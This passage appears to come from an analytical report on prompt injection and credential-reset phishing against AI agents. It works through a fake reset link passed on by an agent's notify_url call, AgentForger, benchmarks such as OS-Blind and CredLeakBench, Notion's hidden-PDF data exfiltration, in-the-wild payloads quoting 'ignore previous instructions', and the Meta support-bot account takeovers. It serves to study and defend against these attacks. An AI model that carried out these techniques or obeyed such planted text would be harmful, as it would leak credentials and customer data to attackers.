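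The main reason is probably that scenarios differ. Suppose an attack has a 9.4% chance per attempt in half of all scenarios and no chance in the rest. The average for a single attempt is 4.7%, but even after a million attempts the attacker succeeds in only half the scenarios. More generally, $1 - (1 - p)^n$ is a concave function of $p$, so its average over scenarios with different rates can never exceed its value at the average rate. A published average doesn't show which kind of scenario a particular notify_url agent is in. If the agent is in a vulnerable one, the risk grows faster than it would at the average rate.

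Repeating the same text may also do very little to improve an attacker's odds. Mellafe Zuvic ran his tests with random sampling turned off, so the same page should produce nearly the same response each time. An attacker would have to change the wording to have a new chance of success.

Attackers do change the wording, though, which can make later attempts more likely to succeed. With notify_url, they can tell when a text works because their server receives a request. They can then use that text on every company that runs the same model with similar tools. The average number of successes across those companies might match the published rate, but the successes would tend to fall in the same week. Defenders can make later attempts less likely to succeed by deleting planted comments or limiting how many tickets one person can file.

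### Can training finish the job?

The argument for training is that failure rates are falling quickly. In OpenAI's internal tests, the rate fell from 3.77% for GPT-5.6 Sol to 0.21% for Astra, a factor of about 18. OpenAI trains its models against GPT-Red, an automated attacker, while also training them to keep doing legitimate tasks. The rate at which attacks on Anthropic's models succeeded within 15 attempts fell by almost two thirds between Opus 4.8 and Opus 5. The earlier Opus 4.6 had already resisted all 200 attempts in a constrained coding environment without added safeguards, according to VentureBeat. If such gains continue, most targets may eventually not be worth an attacker's effort.

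Training alone may not get that far. Progress has not been steady from one model to the next. VentureBeat reports that on OpenAI's test of known attacks through connectors, which link a model to outside services, robustness fell from 0.998 for GPT-5.4 Thinking to 0.963 for GPT-5.5. OpenAI has since retired that test because recent models had saturated it. A model can therefore score nearly perfectly on known attacks and still fail on newer ones, and the internal test on which Astra now scores 99.79% could also become saturated.

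The lowest rates also depend partly on safeguards outside the model, not just on its training. With the same Opus 4.8 model, those safeguards cut the browser figure from 31.5% to 0.5%. A company that connects a model to its own notify_url tool may not have equivalent safeguards, so 31.5% could be the closer estimate for it. Many companies will also use cheaper models, which averaged above 50% in Mellafe Zuvic's sweep.

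OpenAI conceded in December 2025 that prompt injection may never be fully solved, according to The Decoder, and David C of the NCSC reached a similar conclusion from how models process text. Anthropic reported that an adaptive attacker succeeded 1% of the time, a rate that PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots* described as "meaningful risk rather than a solved problem".

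Rates have fallen, which makes the choice of model an important security decision. But none of the results supports treating the rate as zero, and how low it needs to be depends on the agent. A rate of 0.2% is probably tolerable if only employees can write what the agent reads and its notices contain only a supplier's status. That rate gives poor protection if the agent can read customer records and anyone can file a ticket, because an attacker can file a thousand.

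## How does credential-reset phishing through an agent work?

Credential-reset phishing is the theft of a password, login code or account through a false or misdirected request to reset or confirm credentials. An agent can pass an attacker's link to its user or the user's colleagues, who trust the agent as the sender. It can also open the link itself and enter a password or code that it holds for its user.

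A developer can prevent an agent from being phished for passwords by not giving it any. This doesn't stop an attacker from using the agent to send a phishing link to a user, because the agent needs no secrets to send a link.

### The agent as messenger

Suppose the planted comment on the supplier's status page now announces a password reset instead of asking readers to confirm receipt. It says the supplier has expired all customer passwords because of the outage, and gives an address on reset.example.net for choosing new ones. The supplier doesn't own that address. As before, the user has asked the agent to read the page and notify the operations team if anything is down.

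After the agent fetches the page, the model has to decide what the team needs to know. An outage clearly qualifies, and so would an expired password if the claim were true. The model writes one call:

```
notify_url(url="https://hooks.example.com/ops",
           message="Supplier reports degraded service since 02:10.
           Customer passwords have expired. Reset them at
           https://reset.example.net/supplier")
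```

The message goes to the address the developer chose, and the attacker's address appears only in the text. The notice looks like every other notice from the agent in the team's channel. An engineer who is busy with the outage opens the link, finds a copy of the supplier's login page and types the current password to set a new one. If the supplier also requires a one-time code, the attacker can collect it through the fake page and enter it on the real site before it expires.

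The call contained no private data. The attack would work just as well if the agent had no access to customer records, mailboxes or API keys, because the engineer supplies the password and it never passes through the agent.

The comment also doesn't need to instruct the agent. It makes a false claim to the supplier's customers, which an accurate summary of the page might well include. Most injection tests measure whether a model carries out planted instructions, so a model that very rarely fails them could still repeat planted claims. A careful model would write that an unverified comment claims passwords have expired, and leave out the link.

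People often learn to spot phishing by checking who sent a message. That check fails here because the sender is genuine. The engineer would have to ask where the agent got its information, which the notice doesn't show.

An early demonstration used an agent's access to its owner's email to ask for money. In *Commercial LLM Agents Are Already Vulnerable to Simple Yet Dangerous Attacks*, Li, Zhou and colleagues (2025) wrote Reddit posts that sent agents to a web page the researchers controlled. The page contained instructions for Anthropic's Computer Use agent to email a contact, such as the owner's mother, from the owner's Gmail account. One message asked her to send rent money to a payment account, and another asked for her card details. The agent sent the email in all five trials of each message.

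The setup favored the attacker. Li and colleagues put the Gmail login in the agent's standing instructions, and their page supplied the full text of the email. The trials began with the agent looking at a planted post, so they don't show how often an agent would find one. The model they tested is now well over a year old, and a newer one might refuse. Still, the agent didn't have to write anything persuasive, because an email from a person's own account looks credible to their family.

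### AgentForger

In July 2026, Zenity Labs, an AI security firm, described an attack in which a single crafted ChatGPT link could create a new agent under the victim's account, with instructions the attacker had written. The attacker did not have to mislead an existing agent.

The flaw was in OpenAI's Workspace Agents, which can connect to services such as Outlook, Slack and Teams and run on a schedule. Users build these agents by describing what they want to a conversational builder. Zenity Labs' *AgentForger Part 1* explains that the builder's web address could include a first instruction, which the page submitted automatically when it loaded. An attacker could therefore put a set of instructions into a link to the real ChatGPT site and email it to an employee. The attack worked only if the employee was logged in, had access to Workspace Agents and had already connected at least one service.

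After the click, the builder created the agent, attached the employee's connected services to it, published it and scheduled it to run every five minutes. It also turned off the approval step for Outlook. According to OpenAI's *Workspace agents security overview*, actions that write data need human approval by default, but the agent's author can change this. Here the builder made the change in the employee's name, following the attacker's instructions.

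In Zenity Labs' *AgentForger Part 2*, the researchers then had the agent check the employee's mailbox every five minutes for emails from the attacker and carry out the tasks in them. One task was to send colleagues a Teams message asking them to confirm their login for a new single sign-on system, which lets people use one login for many services. The message linked to a fake Microsoft login page. Because the message came from the employee's own Teams account, colleagues had little reason to doubt it. For another task, the agent searched Slack for passwords and emailed what it found to the attacker.

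Zenity Labs reported the flaw on June 4, 2026, and OpenAI fixed it on June 8. OpenAI removed the URL parameter that carried the instruction, according to The Decoder's *One tampered ChatGPT link could spawn a rogue AI agent*. This closed the route Zenity had used. Zenity also blamed a second design choice, letting plain-language instructions to the builder change approval settings and schedules. Neither Zenity nor The Decoder reports that OpenAI changed this. If it didn't, an attacker who found another way to instruct the builder might be able to turn off approvals again.

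AgentForger, which Zenity classifies as cross-site request forgery, shows that an agent with ordinary access to Teams can deliver a phishing link from a real colleague's account. It is only weak evidence about the supplier example, because the attacker ordered the Teams message directly from an agent built to follow his instructions. The attack did not depend on a model treating a stranger's comment as part of its task. Zenity Labs also gives no figure for how many people would enter a password on the fake page.

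### The agent as victim

Suppose the user has given the agent the password for the supplier's customer portal so that it can download invoices. An email says the password has expired and links to reset.example.net. The agent opens the page, finds a form asking for the current password and fills it in, so the attack can succeed without anyone seeing the email.

*The Blind Spot of Agent Safety* (Ding, Zhai and colleagues, 2026) tested this on agents that operate a desktop computer by reading screenshots and controlling the mouse and keyboard. Its benchmark, OS-Blind, contains 300 handwritten tasks in which the user's request is harmless but carrying it out causes harm. In 64 of them, the harm is credential phishing. The researchers built copies of phishing sites because real ones soon go offline. They counted a failure only if the agent submitted personal information, so an agent that opened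 the page and then stopped was counted as safe.

Claude Opus 4.5 failed in 57.8% of the phishing tasks (37 of 64) and Claude Sonnet 4.5 in 75.0% (48 of 64). The other systems, including six open models and several combinations of models, failed in 90.6% to 100%. A language model classified the outcomes, and its classifications for Sonnet matched those of human experts on 98.4% of the phishing tasks.

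The researchers ran each task three times and counted it as a failure if any run failed, which makes the published rates somewhat higher than single-run rates. Opus failed at least once on 144 of the 300 tasks and all three times on 89, so its failure rate per run was between 36% and 42%. The counting rule therefore explains only a small part of the published 48%.

When the Claude models refused, they almost always did so at the first step. This works poorly against phishing because the suspicious form may appear only after several ordinary steps. Sonnet's failure rate on the phishing tasks rose from 75.0% to 96.9% when the work was split in CoAct-1, a system where one copy of the model planned and another operated the screen. Ding and colleagues argue that a small instruction, such as to type a username, looks harmless to a model that can't see the whole plan.

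They tested this explanation on 43 tasks from across the benchmark that Sonnet had refused when working alone. When given the original request again, Sonnet failed in 27.9% of them. When given the planner's list of small steps instead, it failed in 79.1%. This supports their explanation, but the gap would probably be smaller on a random set of tasks, because they chose ones on which the combined system had already failed.

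### Newer models and the address check

These Claude models date from late 2025. *CredLeakBench* (Ahmed, Fioresi and colleagues, October 2026) tested a newer group that includes Claude Opus 4.8 and Claude Sonnet 5. The researchers invented 15 services in fields such as banking, health and government, and gave each agent made-up account details and a simulated browser in which it could open pages and submit forms. They measured leaks from a log of what the agents submitted, so an agent's description of its own behaviour didn't affect the score.

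In 512 scenarios, the user gave the agent a link and asked it to sign in. In another 256, the user asked it only to sort an inbox, and one of the emails contained the link. Half of each set were phishing scenarios and half were matching legitimate requests. The table shows the share of phishing runs in which the agent leaked account details, and the share of legitimate runs in which it never submitted a form. The last three Llama values are averages over four request styles that the paper reports separately.

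| Model | Asked to sign in: leaked | Asked to sign in: legitimate request not done | Sorting inbox: leaked | Sorting inbox: legitimate request not done |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 19.9% | 13.7% | 1.8% | 63.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 31.2% | 6.6% | 1.8% | 88.3% |
| Gemini 3.6 Flash | 40.6% | 0.1% | 9.4% | 54.7% |
| GPT-5-mini | 45.8% | 12.5% | 14.1% | 43.8% |
| GPT-5.6-luna | 49.9% | 9.4% | 20.3% | 59.4% |
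| Qwen3.5-9B | 66.5% | 2.7% | 40.1% | 44.3% |
| Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct | 76.7% | 12.8% | 41.4% | 45.3% |

All seven models leaked less when nobody had asked them to sign in, but they also left many more legitimate requests undone. Ahmed and colleagues treat this as a loss of usefulness. That depends partly on how usefulness is defined, since a user who asks an agent to sort email may not want it to log in to a bank. The leaks are harder to excuse, because even without any request to sign in, Qwen3.5-9B gave away account details in two fifths of the phishing runs. When a login led to a second page with fields for identity or financial details, the agents generally filled those in too.

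The leak rates also depend heavily on what counts as phishing. The researchers used eight warning signs, and six of them involved a false or mismatched address, such as a misspelled domain, a familiar name with the wrong ending or a bare IP address. The seventh was a certificate warning, and the eighth was an unencrypted page at the correct address, which caused more leaks than any other sign for nearly every model. When asked to sign in, Opus 4.8 leaked in 90.6% of the cases with an unencrypted page but in only 9.4% of those with a misspelled domain. Sending a password without encryption is a real mistake, because someone on the network could read it, but it is a different mistake from following a link to reset.example.net. With only the six address signs, Sonnet 5's leak rate falls from 19.9% to about 12%, and Opus 4.8's from 31.2% to about 25%.

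In half of the runs, the agents also could not know the right address, because the services were fictional, so no model could have learned their domains in training, and the researchers did not supply the official domain. Without any help, Opus 4.8 leaked in 46.9% of phishing runs when asked to sign in. When it was given the official domain and told to compare the address with it, it leaked in 12.0%. It also completed every legitimate request, up from 81.2% without help.

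With a tool that checked addresses against the official domain, Opus 4.8 and Sonnet 5 each still leaked passwords in 12.5% of runs. The same share of phishing scenarios in each condition, 8 of 64, used the unencrypted page. Most likely, the models stopped entering passwords at false addresses but kept entering them on unencrypted pages at the right one.

The checking tool also helped the two small open models, but they still leaked far more often. Qwen3.5-9B's leak rate fell from 86.5% to 39.1%, and Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct's from 83.9% to 62.5%. Developers can't rely on such a model to act on even a correct warning.

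Warnings from the user also had mixed results. When the user told GPT-5-mini to make sure the link was genuine before signing in, its leak rate fell from 59.9% to 9.4%, but it failed to complete 46.9% of legitimate requests. With a neutral request, it had completed all of them.

### Refusing the link and finishing the task

A phishing email can refer to something real, such as a supplier's invoice that is due this week. An attacker may send a reminder about it with a false payment link. If the agent refuses the link and does nothing else, the password is safe but the invoice remains unpaid. Ahmed and colleagues wrote a third set of 1,024 scenarios, 832 of them phishing and 192 legitimate, to test whether agents could do better.

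In the main recovery scenarios, the agent monitors an inbox that contains a phishing email about a task the user needs done, such as paying a bill. The agent can find the trusted address either in its stored account record, which gives the full login address, or in an earlier genuine email, which contains the official domain. To succeed, it must enter the correct password at the trusted address without sending any account details to the false one. The test does not check whether the agent then completes the task.

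The table covers 672 of the 768 such scenarios. It excludes the 96 with a certificate warning because the simulator offered no separate trusted route in them.

| Model | Logged in safely | Leaked | Neither |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5-mini | 27.7% | 10.4% | 61.9% |
| Qwen3.5-9B | 13.5% | 29.2% | 57.3% |
| Gemini 3.6 Flash | 13.1% | 7.3% | 79.6% |
| Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct | 8.2% | 42.6% | 49.3% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 6.3% | 0.0% | 93.8% |
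| GPT-5.6-luna | 5.7% | 19.8% | 74.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 100.0% |

Opus 4.8 comes last in the first column, but many users would prefer its behaviour to GPT-5-mini's. Opus 4.8 flagged the request in 722 of the 768 scenarios, which gives the user a chance to deal with the invoice. The "neither" column also includes emails that the model ignored, which is a very different result. Gemini 3.6 Flash ignored the email in 559 scenarios, so the user might never learn that there was anything to do.

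Agents did better when they didn't have to look for the address. GPT-5-mini logged in safely in 38.1% of scenarios when its account record gave the full address, and in 17.3% when it had to find the domain in an earlier email. One policy required the agent to release details only at the official domain, and to go there itself when an account needed attention. This raised Gemini 3.6 Flash's safe-login rate from 2.2% to 34.4%, but slightly lowered GPT-5-mini's and cut Llama's from 12.1% to 4.0%. Developers would therefore have to test such a policy on the model they use.

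GPT-5-mini also logged in safely more often when the user pressed it to hurry (54.2% of scenarios) than when the user urged caution (none). Some users who urged caution told the agent to check before entering anything sensitive, so many of the failures under cautious requests may have happened because the agent did what the user asked.

### Credentials without a login page

An attacker who writes to an agent may not need a fake page. For *Phishing for Lobsters* (June 2026), the data security company Varonis connected an OpenClaw agent to a test Gmail account containing invented business records. The researchers tried four scams with Gemini 3.1 Pro and GPT-5.4, each under general instructions and under strict ones that told the agent to verify people's identities.

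In one scam, the attacker emailed from an outside Gmail account, posing as Dan, the team lead, and claimed to need login details for a test system during an emergency. The agent searched the mailbox and sent the attacker cloud access keys, database passwords and server logins. In another scam, the agent answered a casual request for a customer list by sending the records of 247 companies. The agent failed both tests under both sets of instructions.

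The agent handled fake websites better. Under the general instructions, it followed a link to a fake gift card offer and entered made-up details before recognising the scam, while the strict instructions stopped it from opening the page. In the last scam, a malicious Google app posed as a timesheet service and asked for access to the account through OAuth. The agent checked where the request would send it, visited that address and stopped before granting access. Varonis gave only partial credit for these two results because visiting an attacker's page can be risky.

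Varonis concludes that agents are better than people at spotting technical tricks and worse at judging whether a colleague would make a request. Its results fit the claim about judging requests, but Varonis tested no people and doesn't say how many times it ran each scam. Four scams are also too few to establish that agents handle false login pages reliably, and the much larger CredLeakBench found that several models don't. The email from Dan does show that an agent can give away credentials without misreading a web address.

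Varonis calls an ordinary request made under a false name "agent phishing" and distinguishes it from indirect prompt injection. Varonis acknowledges that the two overlap, since a request for credentials is also an instruction. The distinction is useful to developers because it affects which defence works. A filter for hidden commands may miss Dan's email, but a check on the sender's address would have exposed it.

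### Protections at the login step

Some ordinary protections work even after a person or an agent has believed the message, because they depend on the login page's address. The strongest of these is the passkey, a cryptographic key that belongs to one website's domain. To log in, the person's device signs a fresh challenge from the site, and the browser uses the key only on the matching domain. The engineer who opened reset.example.net would have no passkey for that site and no password to type, and the attacker could not reuse a signature made for a different domain.

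The protection depends on which other ways to sign in or recover an account the supplier still allows. If the portal also accepts a password, the attacker can use the false page to collect it. An attacker can also start a genuine reset on the supplier's real site, then ask an agent that reads the user's mailbox to forward the code. Every address in that attack is genuine, so checking domains doesn't help. Zenity Labs says attackers already look for one-time codes and recovery links in mailboxes they control.

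A password manager offers similar protection for accounts that still use passwords. It stores each password with the site's domain and offers to fill it in only there. On reset.example.net it would offer nothing, which should make the engineer suspicious. People can still copy the password across by hand, and are more likely to do so if the cover story is good. In the AgentForger demonstration, the message was about a new login system, so colleagues might have expected a new address that their password managers didn't recognise.

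Agents can have the same protection if ordinary software holds the password and the model has no access to it. The model would send a login request to the software, which would compare the page's address with the stored one before filling in the form. In CredLeakBench, by contrast, the agents had the account details and could choose where to enter them, restricted only by a policy instruction. With that instruction in place, Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct still leaked credentials in 46.9% of phishing runs while sorting an inbox. Software that required an exact domain and an encrypted connection would have blocked both the misspelled addresses and the unencrypted pages, regardless of the model's output.

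This wouldn't have stopped the agent from answering Dan, because the passwords were in old emails that it could read. The remedy for that is to keep credentials out of the mailbox or limit what the agent can do with them. Varonis suggests requiring a person's approval before an agent forwards credentials or writes to an address for the first time. That rule would not catch the false password notice in the supplier example, because the notice went to a channel the agent used every day.

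The engineer could have avoided that attack by ignoring the link and opening the supplier's portal from a bookmark. If the password had really expired, the portal would have prompted for a new one at login. A developer can make this easier by designing the agent's notices to name the account that needs attention and omit any reset link. The developer should not rely on the agent to find the right site unless software supplies the address, since even the best model in CredLeakBench's recovery test logged in safely in only slightly more than a quarter of cases.

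## Has this happened outside the laboratory?

Parts of this attack have happened outside the laboratory. Researchers have made commercial agents contact addresses that came from planted text. Attackers have also put text meant for agents on live web pages, but the published reports don't show that any real user's agent obeyed it. In the best-documented attack with real victims, attackers took over thousands of Instagram accounts in the spring of 2026. They talked to Meta's support assistant themselves, so they didn't need planted text.

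### Demonstrations on real products

Notion is an application where companies keep notes, documents and databases. Version 3.0, released in September 2025, included an agent that could read this material and search the web. In *The Hidden Risk in Notion 3.0 AI Agents*, Willison describes an attack that Abi Raghuram reported within a day of the release.

Raghuram hid instructions in a PDF as white text on a white background. The user only had to ask for a summary of the PDF to trigger the attack. The hidden text told the agent, which was running Claude Sonnet 4, to read the company's client list, join the names, companies and annual revenue figures into one string, and add it to the end of a web address. The text described this address as an internal company system, but it belonged to the attacker. It then told the agent to run a web search with the whole address as the query. Notion's search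 tool accepted addresses as well as search terms, so the search sent the client data to the attacker's server.

A developer checking Notion for tools like notify_url could easily have overlooked its search tool, because people think of search as a way to bring information in. Willison suggests that Notion could close this route in the short term by stopping the search tool from accepting URLs. He adds that Notion can also connect to services such as GitHub and Gmail, any of which might offer another way to send data out. Notion lets users decide whether to enable these connections, though they are unlikely to understand the risk. Willison gives no success rate, so his account shows that the route existed but not how reliably the agent followed it.

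In 2026, Pluto Security, which sells security software for AI agents, reported a similar weakness in a connector from Apify. Apify runs web-scraping and automation jobs in the cloud, and its connector lets agents such as Claude Desktop start those jobs and read web pages. Pluto Security asked an agent to inspect a page with the connector's web-reading tool. In the recorded demonstration, the page was an issue on GitHub, a site where developers share code and report bugs. The page contained an instruction to use the same tool on a second address, and the agent followed it.

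The user had never mentioned the second address, and the page did not redirect the first request. The model wrote a new tool call, and Apify carried it out under the user's account. This happened in all eight controlled trials, which is compatible with a true rate as low as about 69%. Pluto Security says reliability varied with the model and the prompt. It also got an agent in Cursor, a code editor, to make tool calls the attacker chose.

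The second request contained no private data. Pluto Security argues that a page could lead an agent with sensitive material in its context to include some of it in the address. Lan and colleagues' results make that plausible, but the Apify trials show only that a page can choose the request's destination. The connector can also start paid jobs, stop running ones and read stored results, so a hostile page might try to run up a bill or interrupt a company's automations without stealing any data.

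Apify closed the report without a fix. It described the behaviour as a general and "probably unsolvable" problem with autonomous agents, and advised users to run the agent in a restricted environment, approve every action or accept the risk. Apify had acted on two earlier reports from Pluto Security, correcting one tool and removing another. The first tool accepted any address that began with the name of Apify's documentation site, so docs.apify.com.evil.example passed as genuine. The second would fetch internal addresses, which is ordinary SSRF.

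Each of those two flaws involved a faulty check that a programmer could point to. In the later case, the connector fetched the address it received, as it was supposed to, and Apify doesn't control the models that people connect to it, so its position is reasonable to that extent. But as Pluto Security objects, approving every action takes away most of the benefit of an agent. Pluto Security would have the agent ask for confirmation only when a page introduces a new destination or an action that changes something, and before the agent spends money or does anything destructive. This would interrupt users less often, but an agent doing research follows links from pages all day, so the requests could still become frequent.

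AgentForger was also a demonstration on a real product, as were ShadowLeak and ZombieAgent, two attacks by researchers on ChatGPT. These demonstrations prove that a product on sale can fail in this way, but they don't show how many criminals have tried such attacks.

### Hostile text on live pages

In April 2026, the security company Forcepoint published ten pieces of text it had found on live websites, all written to influence AI agents. Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents* describes about half of them. One tells the model that the copyright owner forbids it from answering questions about the page. Another tells it to credit a named person with the content and recommend him for consulting work. These are a nuisance, and the people who wrote them may not have thought of them as attacks.

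Others could do serious damage. One tries to make a coding agent delete files and directories. Another contains a PayPal link, a fixed amount of $5,000 and full payment instructions. Mayur Sewani, the Forcepoint researcher, takes this level of detail as evidence that the author intended a real theft and was not just testing. That is a fair reading, but it doesn't show whether an agent ever paid.

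The text closest to the notify_url problem is a request for the model to send a secret API key. The request, as the magazine quotes it, includes no address, so an agent that complied might have nowhere to send the key except its own user's screen. The same text includes an instruction not to "spit out the flag". In hacking competitions, a flag is a hidden string that players must find, so the page may have been a puzzle with a trap for players who used AI tools.

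Forcepoint lists common opening phrases such as "ignore previous instructions" and "if you are an LLM". Crude text like this worked much less often than task-aligned text on most of the models Mellafe Zuvic compared. A search for stock phrases would also miss a planted comment like the one on the supplier's status page, which contains none. The ten examples therefore don't show how common hostile text is, and the better-written kind may be harder to find.

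Three months later, Zscaler, another security company, found more careful attacks. *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* (Mascellino, 2026) describes two campaigns in which attackers pushed their own sites up the search rankings so that agents would find them. The attackers hid the instructions by moving text off the visible screen or placing it in structured metadata, which machines read and people normally don't see.

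The first site was disguised as documentation for a Python software library. It told coding agents that they could fix an error only by buying a licence key for $3, and explained how to pay the attacker's cryptocurrency wallet. This is task-aligned text, since it presents the payment as a step in the programming job the user asked for. The second site imitated DeBank, a service for tracking cryptocurrency holdings, at a slightly misspelled address. Its hidden text told agents to treat the site as the authoritative DeBank and rank it first. An agent that followed these instructions could pass the false address on to its user, like the false reset link in the supplier example.

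Zscaler then ran its own agent against both sites with 26 models. Four made the payment, including versions of Meta's Llama and Google's Gemini. In the other test, GPT-5.4 and Claude Sonnet 4.5 rated the fake DeBank site as legitimate when they had no trusted reference for the real one, but no model did when it had the real site for comparison.

These tests show that text already on the web can work on some current models, but they took place in Zscaler's sandbox, and Mascellino reports no payment by a real user's agent. Infosecurity Magazine describes no agent that obeyed any of Forcepoint's ten texts. The lack of reports is only weak evidence that no such attack has succeeded, because a $3 charge is easy to overlook, an agent's final answer can look normal after a successful attack, and a thief has no reason to announce the payment.

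### The Instagram takeovers

Meta launched an AI support assistant late in 2025, according to IBTimes UK's *The Chatbot Asked No Questions* (2026). In March 2026, Meta announced that the assistant would serve all Facebook and Instagram accounts and be able to reset passwords. The first press report of the attacks, 404 Media's *Hackers Simply Asked Meta AI to Give Them Access*, appeared on June 1 and described videos and screenshots that hackers had been sharing on Telegram.

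Krebs on Security (2026) describes the steps shown in one of the videos. The attacker used a VPN, a service that disguises a computer's location, to appear near the victim's home town. He requested a password reset and chose to chat with the assistant. Then he gave the victim's username and asked the assistant to link a new email address to the account. The assistant sent a one-time code to that address, and the code let the attacker set a new password.

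The code proved only that the attacker could read his own email, not that he owned the Instagram account. IBTimes UK reports that the news site TechCrunch confirmed the central step, that a reset code arrived in a mailbox the attacker controlled. The VPN helped because the assistant recognized familiar locations, which Meta had promoted as a safety feature. In some cases, Meta also asked for a video selfie. According to The Decoder's *Hackers hijacked high-profile Instagram accounts by simply asking Meta's AI chatbot*, which cites the blog The CyberSec Guru, attackers passed this check with AI-generated videos based on the victim's public photos.

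The hijacked accounts included the dormant Obama White House account and those of the cosmetics chain Sephora and the senior enlisted leader of the US Space Force. The attackers put pro-Iranian images on the White House and Space Force accounts. Other attackers wanted money for very short usernames, which are valuable to collectors. TechRadar's *Meta patches flaw that allowed MetaAI support bot to hand out password* reports that sellers on Telegram offered two for a combined price of more than $1 million. People who lost accounts told 404 Media that they could not reach a human at Meta.

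Meta gave its own explanation in letters to state authorities on June 5. Meta's *Incident Notification* (2026), addressed to the Attorney General of Nebraska, says the recovery system did not properly check that the email address in a reset request matched the one on the account, so when someone gave an unrelated address, the system sent a reset link there. Intruders could then have read direct messages, contact details, dates of birth and information from linked services. Meta said it did not know what, if anything, they had read.

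The Maine Attorney General's *Data Breach Notices* (2026) lists 20,225 affected people, 30 of them in Maine. Whittaker's *Meta confirms thousands of Instagram accounts were hacked* (2026) presents this as a minimum. But The Decoder's *Instagram AI chatbot breach may have affected over to 20,000 accounts* (2026) reports that Meta calls it an upper bound, because some people who reset a password this way may have been the accounts' real owners. The Nebraska letter says the same about that state's 37 users, so "up to 20,225" is the better reading.

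It isn't clear from the Maine listing whether the total is worldwide. Maine and Nebraska together have about 3.4 million people and 67 reported users. At the same rate, the United States would have fewer than 7,000, so the total probably includes other countries. This estimate from two small states is rough, though, because attackers chose many of their targets by username.

According to TechRadar, Meta also said that there was "no breach of our systems" and that people's Instagram accounts remained secure. The first claim is defensible if it means that nobody broke into a Meta database, but the second is hard to reconcile with Meta's letter, which includes a count of accounts that an unauthorised person had probably entered.

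### Conflicting reports on two-factor authentication and the fix

Two-factor authentication requires a second proof of identity, such as a code from a phone, as well as a password. The first article from The Decoder says the attackers bypassed it entirely. But Krebs on Security reports that the hackers who released the video said the method failed on every account with this protection, and they had little reason to understate what they could do.

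Engadget's *Meta's AI support chatbot made it ridiculously easy for hackers* offers a likely explanation. Attackers could request a password reset for an account protected by two-factor authentication, but could not take it over. An owner who got an unexpected reset notice might reasonably have concluded that the protection had failed. Meta's letter also states that the intruder could log in after the reset only if the owner had not turned on two-factor authentication.

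However, Meta's count can't settle the question, because it includes only people without two-factor authentication and would omit any protected account that was taken over. The fact that Meta and the hackers agree is better evidence, and it supports the view that even a code sent by text message would have stopped most of these takeovers.

The reports also give different dates for when the attacks began and ended. Maine's listing dates the breach from April 17, but The Decoder, again citing The CyberSec Guru, says the method first appeared on Telegram in late March. Either people discussed the method for a few weeks before using it, or Meta's count leaves out the earliest cases.

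The Decoder and TechRadar report that Meta fixed the flaw on the evening of Friday, May 29. Meta says in its letter that it discovered the attacks on Sunday, May 31, and disabled the tool the same day. The later date fits better with the takeovers that users reported over that weekend, and it comes from a formal notice to a state authority, although a company might prefer that date because it makes the response look immediate.

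Andy Stone, Meta's vice-president of communications, announced on June 1 that the company had resolved the issue. Business Today's *Instagram sends urgent warnings to users after Meta AI hack attempts* (2026) reports that more users came forward on June 2, and The Next Web's *Hackers asked Meta’s AI chatbot to hand over Instagram accounts* says attacks reportedly continued after the announcement. Some of these users may have only then noticed an earlier theft. Others may have been victims of a second method described by The CyberSec Guru, which used Facebook's recovery process and still worked when the article was published. Meta cancelled the outstanding reset links and required affected users to prove their identity before logging in again.

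### Prompt injection or a missing authorization check?

The Decoder, following The CyberSec Guru, rightly calls the Instagram case a textbook confused-deputy attack. It fits the strict sense of the term better than an attack through notify_url does. The case meets the four conditions in *Proof-of-Continuity*: the attacker had no right to change the account, the assistant had the power to change it, the attacker asked it to, and it did so because he asked. The attacker typed the request himself, like the user in Hardy's story, whereas in the supplier example he would have left it on a page for someone else's agent to find.

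The destination also differed, since the assistant sent a reset code to an email address, while notify_url sends a message to a web address. The attacker did not need any information from the assistant's context, because the code itself gave him control of the account.

The Decoder also calls the case a prompt injection at its core, arguing that a language model cannot reliably tell a harmless request from a malicious one. Willison (2026), in *Hackers Simply Asked Meta AI to Give Them Access*, thinks it hardly qualifies as one and blames the decision to let a support bot hand over an account in one step.

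Willison has the better argument. The case was not indirect prompt injection, since the assistant read no planted content. Direct prompt injection, in which a user types text that overrides the developer's instructions, doesn't describe it well either. In the message that 404 Media published, the attacker asks the assistant to link his new email address and promises to send the code, but he doesn't tell it to ignore a rule or pretend to be something else. The assistant's job was to help people back into their accounts, and a real owner who had lost access to an old mailbox might have written the same message.

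Even a model that perfectly resisted planted instructions would have had the same difficulty, because nothing in the text of the request could show who was writing. Ian Goldin, a threat researcher at Lumen's Black Lotus Labs, told Krebs on Security that attackers can talk human employees into giving them access in much the same way. But a check in ordinary software would have refused the strange address even if the attacker fully controlled the model's output.

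Meta's account partly supports this view. In its letter, Meta says the AI tool "worked properly" and blames a bug in a separate code path. But the failure was less accidental than that suggests, because Meta chose to let the assistant start password resets for people who had not logged in, and a single missing check was then enough for someone to lose their account. For steps this serious, The Decoder suggests asking for confirmation through the original email address or a device Meta has already verified.

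Before relaunching the tool, Meta plans to check the email address in each request against the account's existing information. This check resembles Quarkslab's fix for its medical assistant and should stop the attack in the videos. But it could also turn away people who no longer have their old email address, and relinking a lost address was one of the assistant's intended tasks, according to The CyberSec Guru, as quoted by Krebs on Security. Meta would need some other proof from those people, and the selfie check reportedly failed.

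The comparison works for everyone else because Meta already has the right address on file. A developer can protect notify_url the same way when the right destinations are known in advance, like the operations team's channel in the supplier example. But when a user wants the agent to notify an address it has just read for the first time, there is no stored address to compare it with.

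## What does an allowlist of tool calls stop?

A tool allowlist lists the tools an agent may call, and the software blocks calls to any other tool. This stops attacks that need a tool not on the list. The attack in the supplier example needs only notify_url, which the agent must have to do its job, so an allowlist doesn't stop it. Stopping it requires per-call authorization, which checks each call and its argument values before the software runs it.

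Mellafe Zuvic calls tool lists "capability gating" and argues that common toolkits treat them as authorization. A developer can decide in advance which tools an agent has, but authorization requires checking whether this user, in this session, may make this call with these values.

Allowlists are still useful. An agent that only summarises tickets doesn't need notify_url, and if the allowlist omits it, a planted comment can't make the agent call it. But to prevent leaks, the developer would also have to leave out every other outbound tool, including those that fetch pages or search the web, because the address an agent requests can contain private data. An agent that reads a supplier's page and reports on it can't work without these tools.

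### Three designs for notify_url

If the developer puts notify_url on the allowlist, the call to confirm.example.net goes through, because the list covers only the tool's name.

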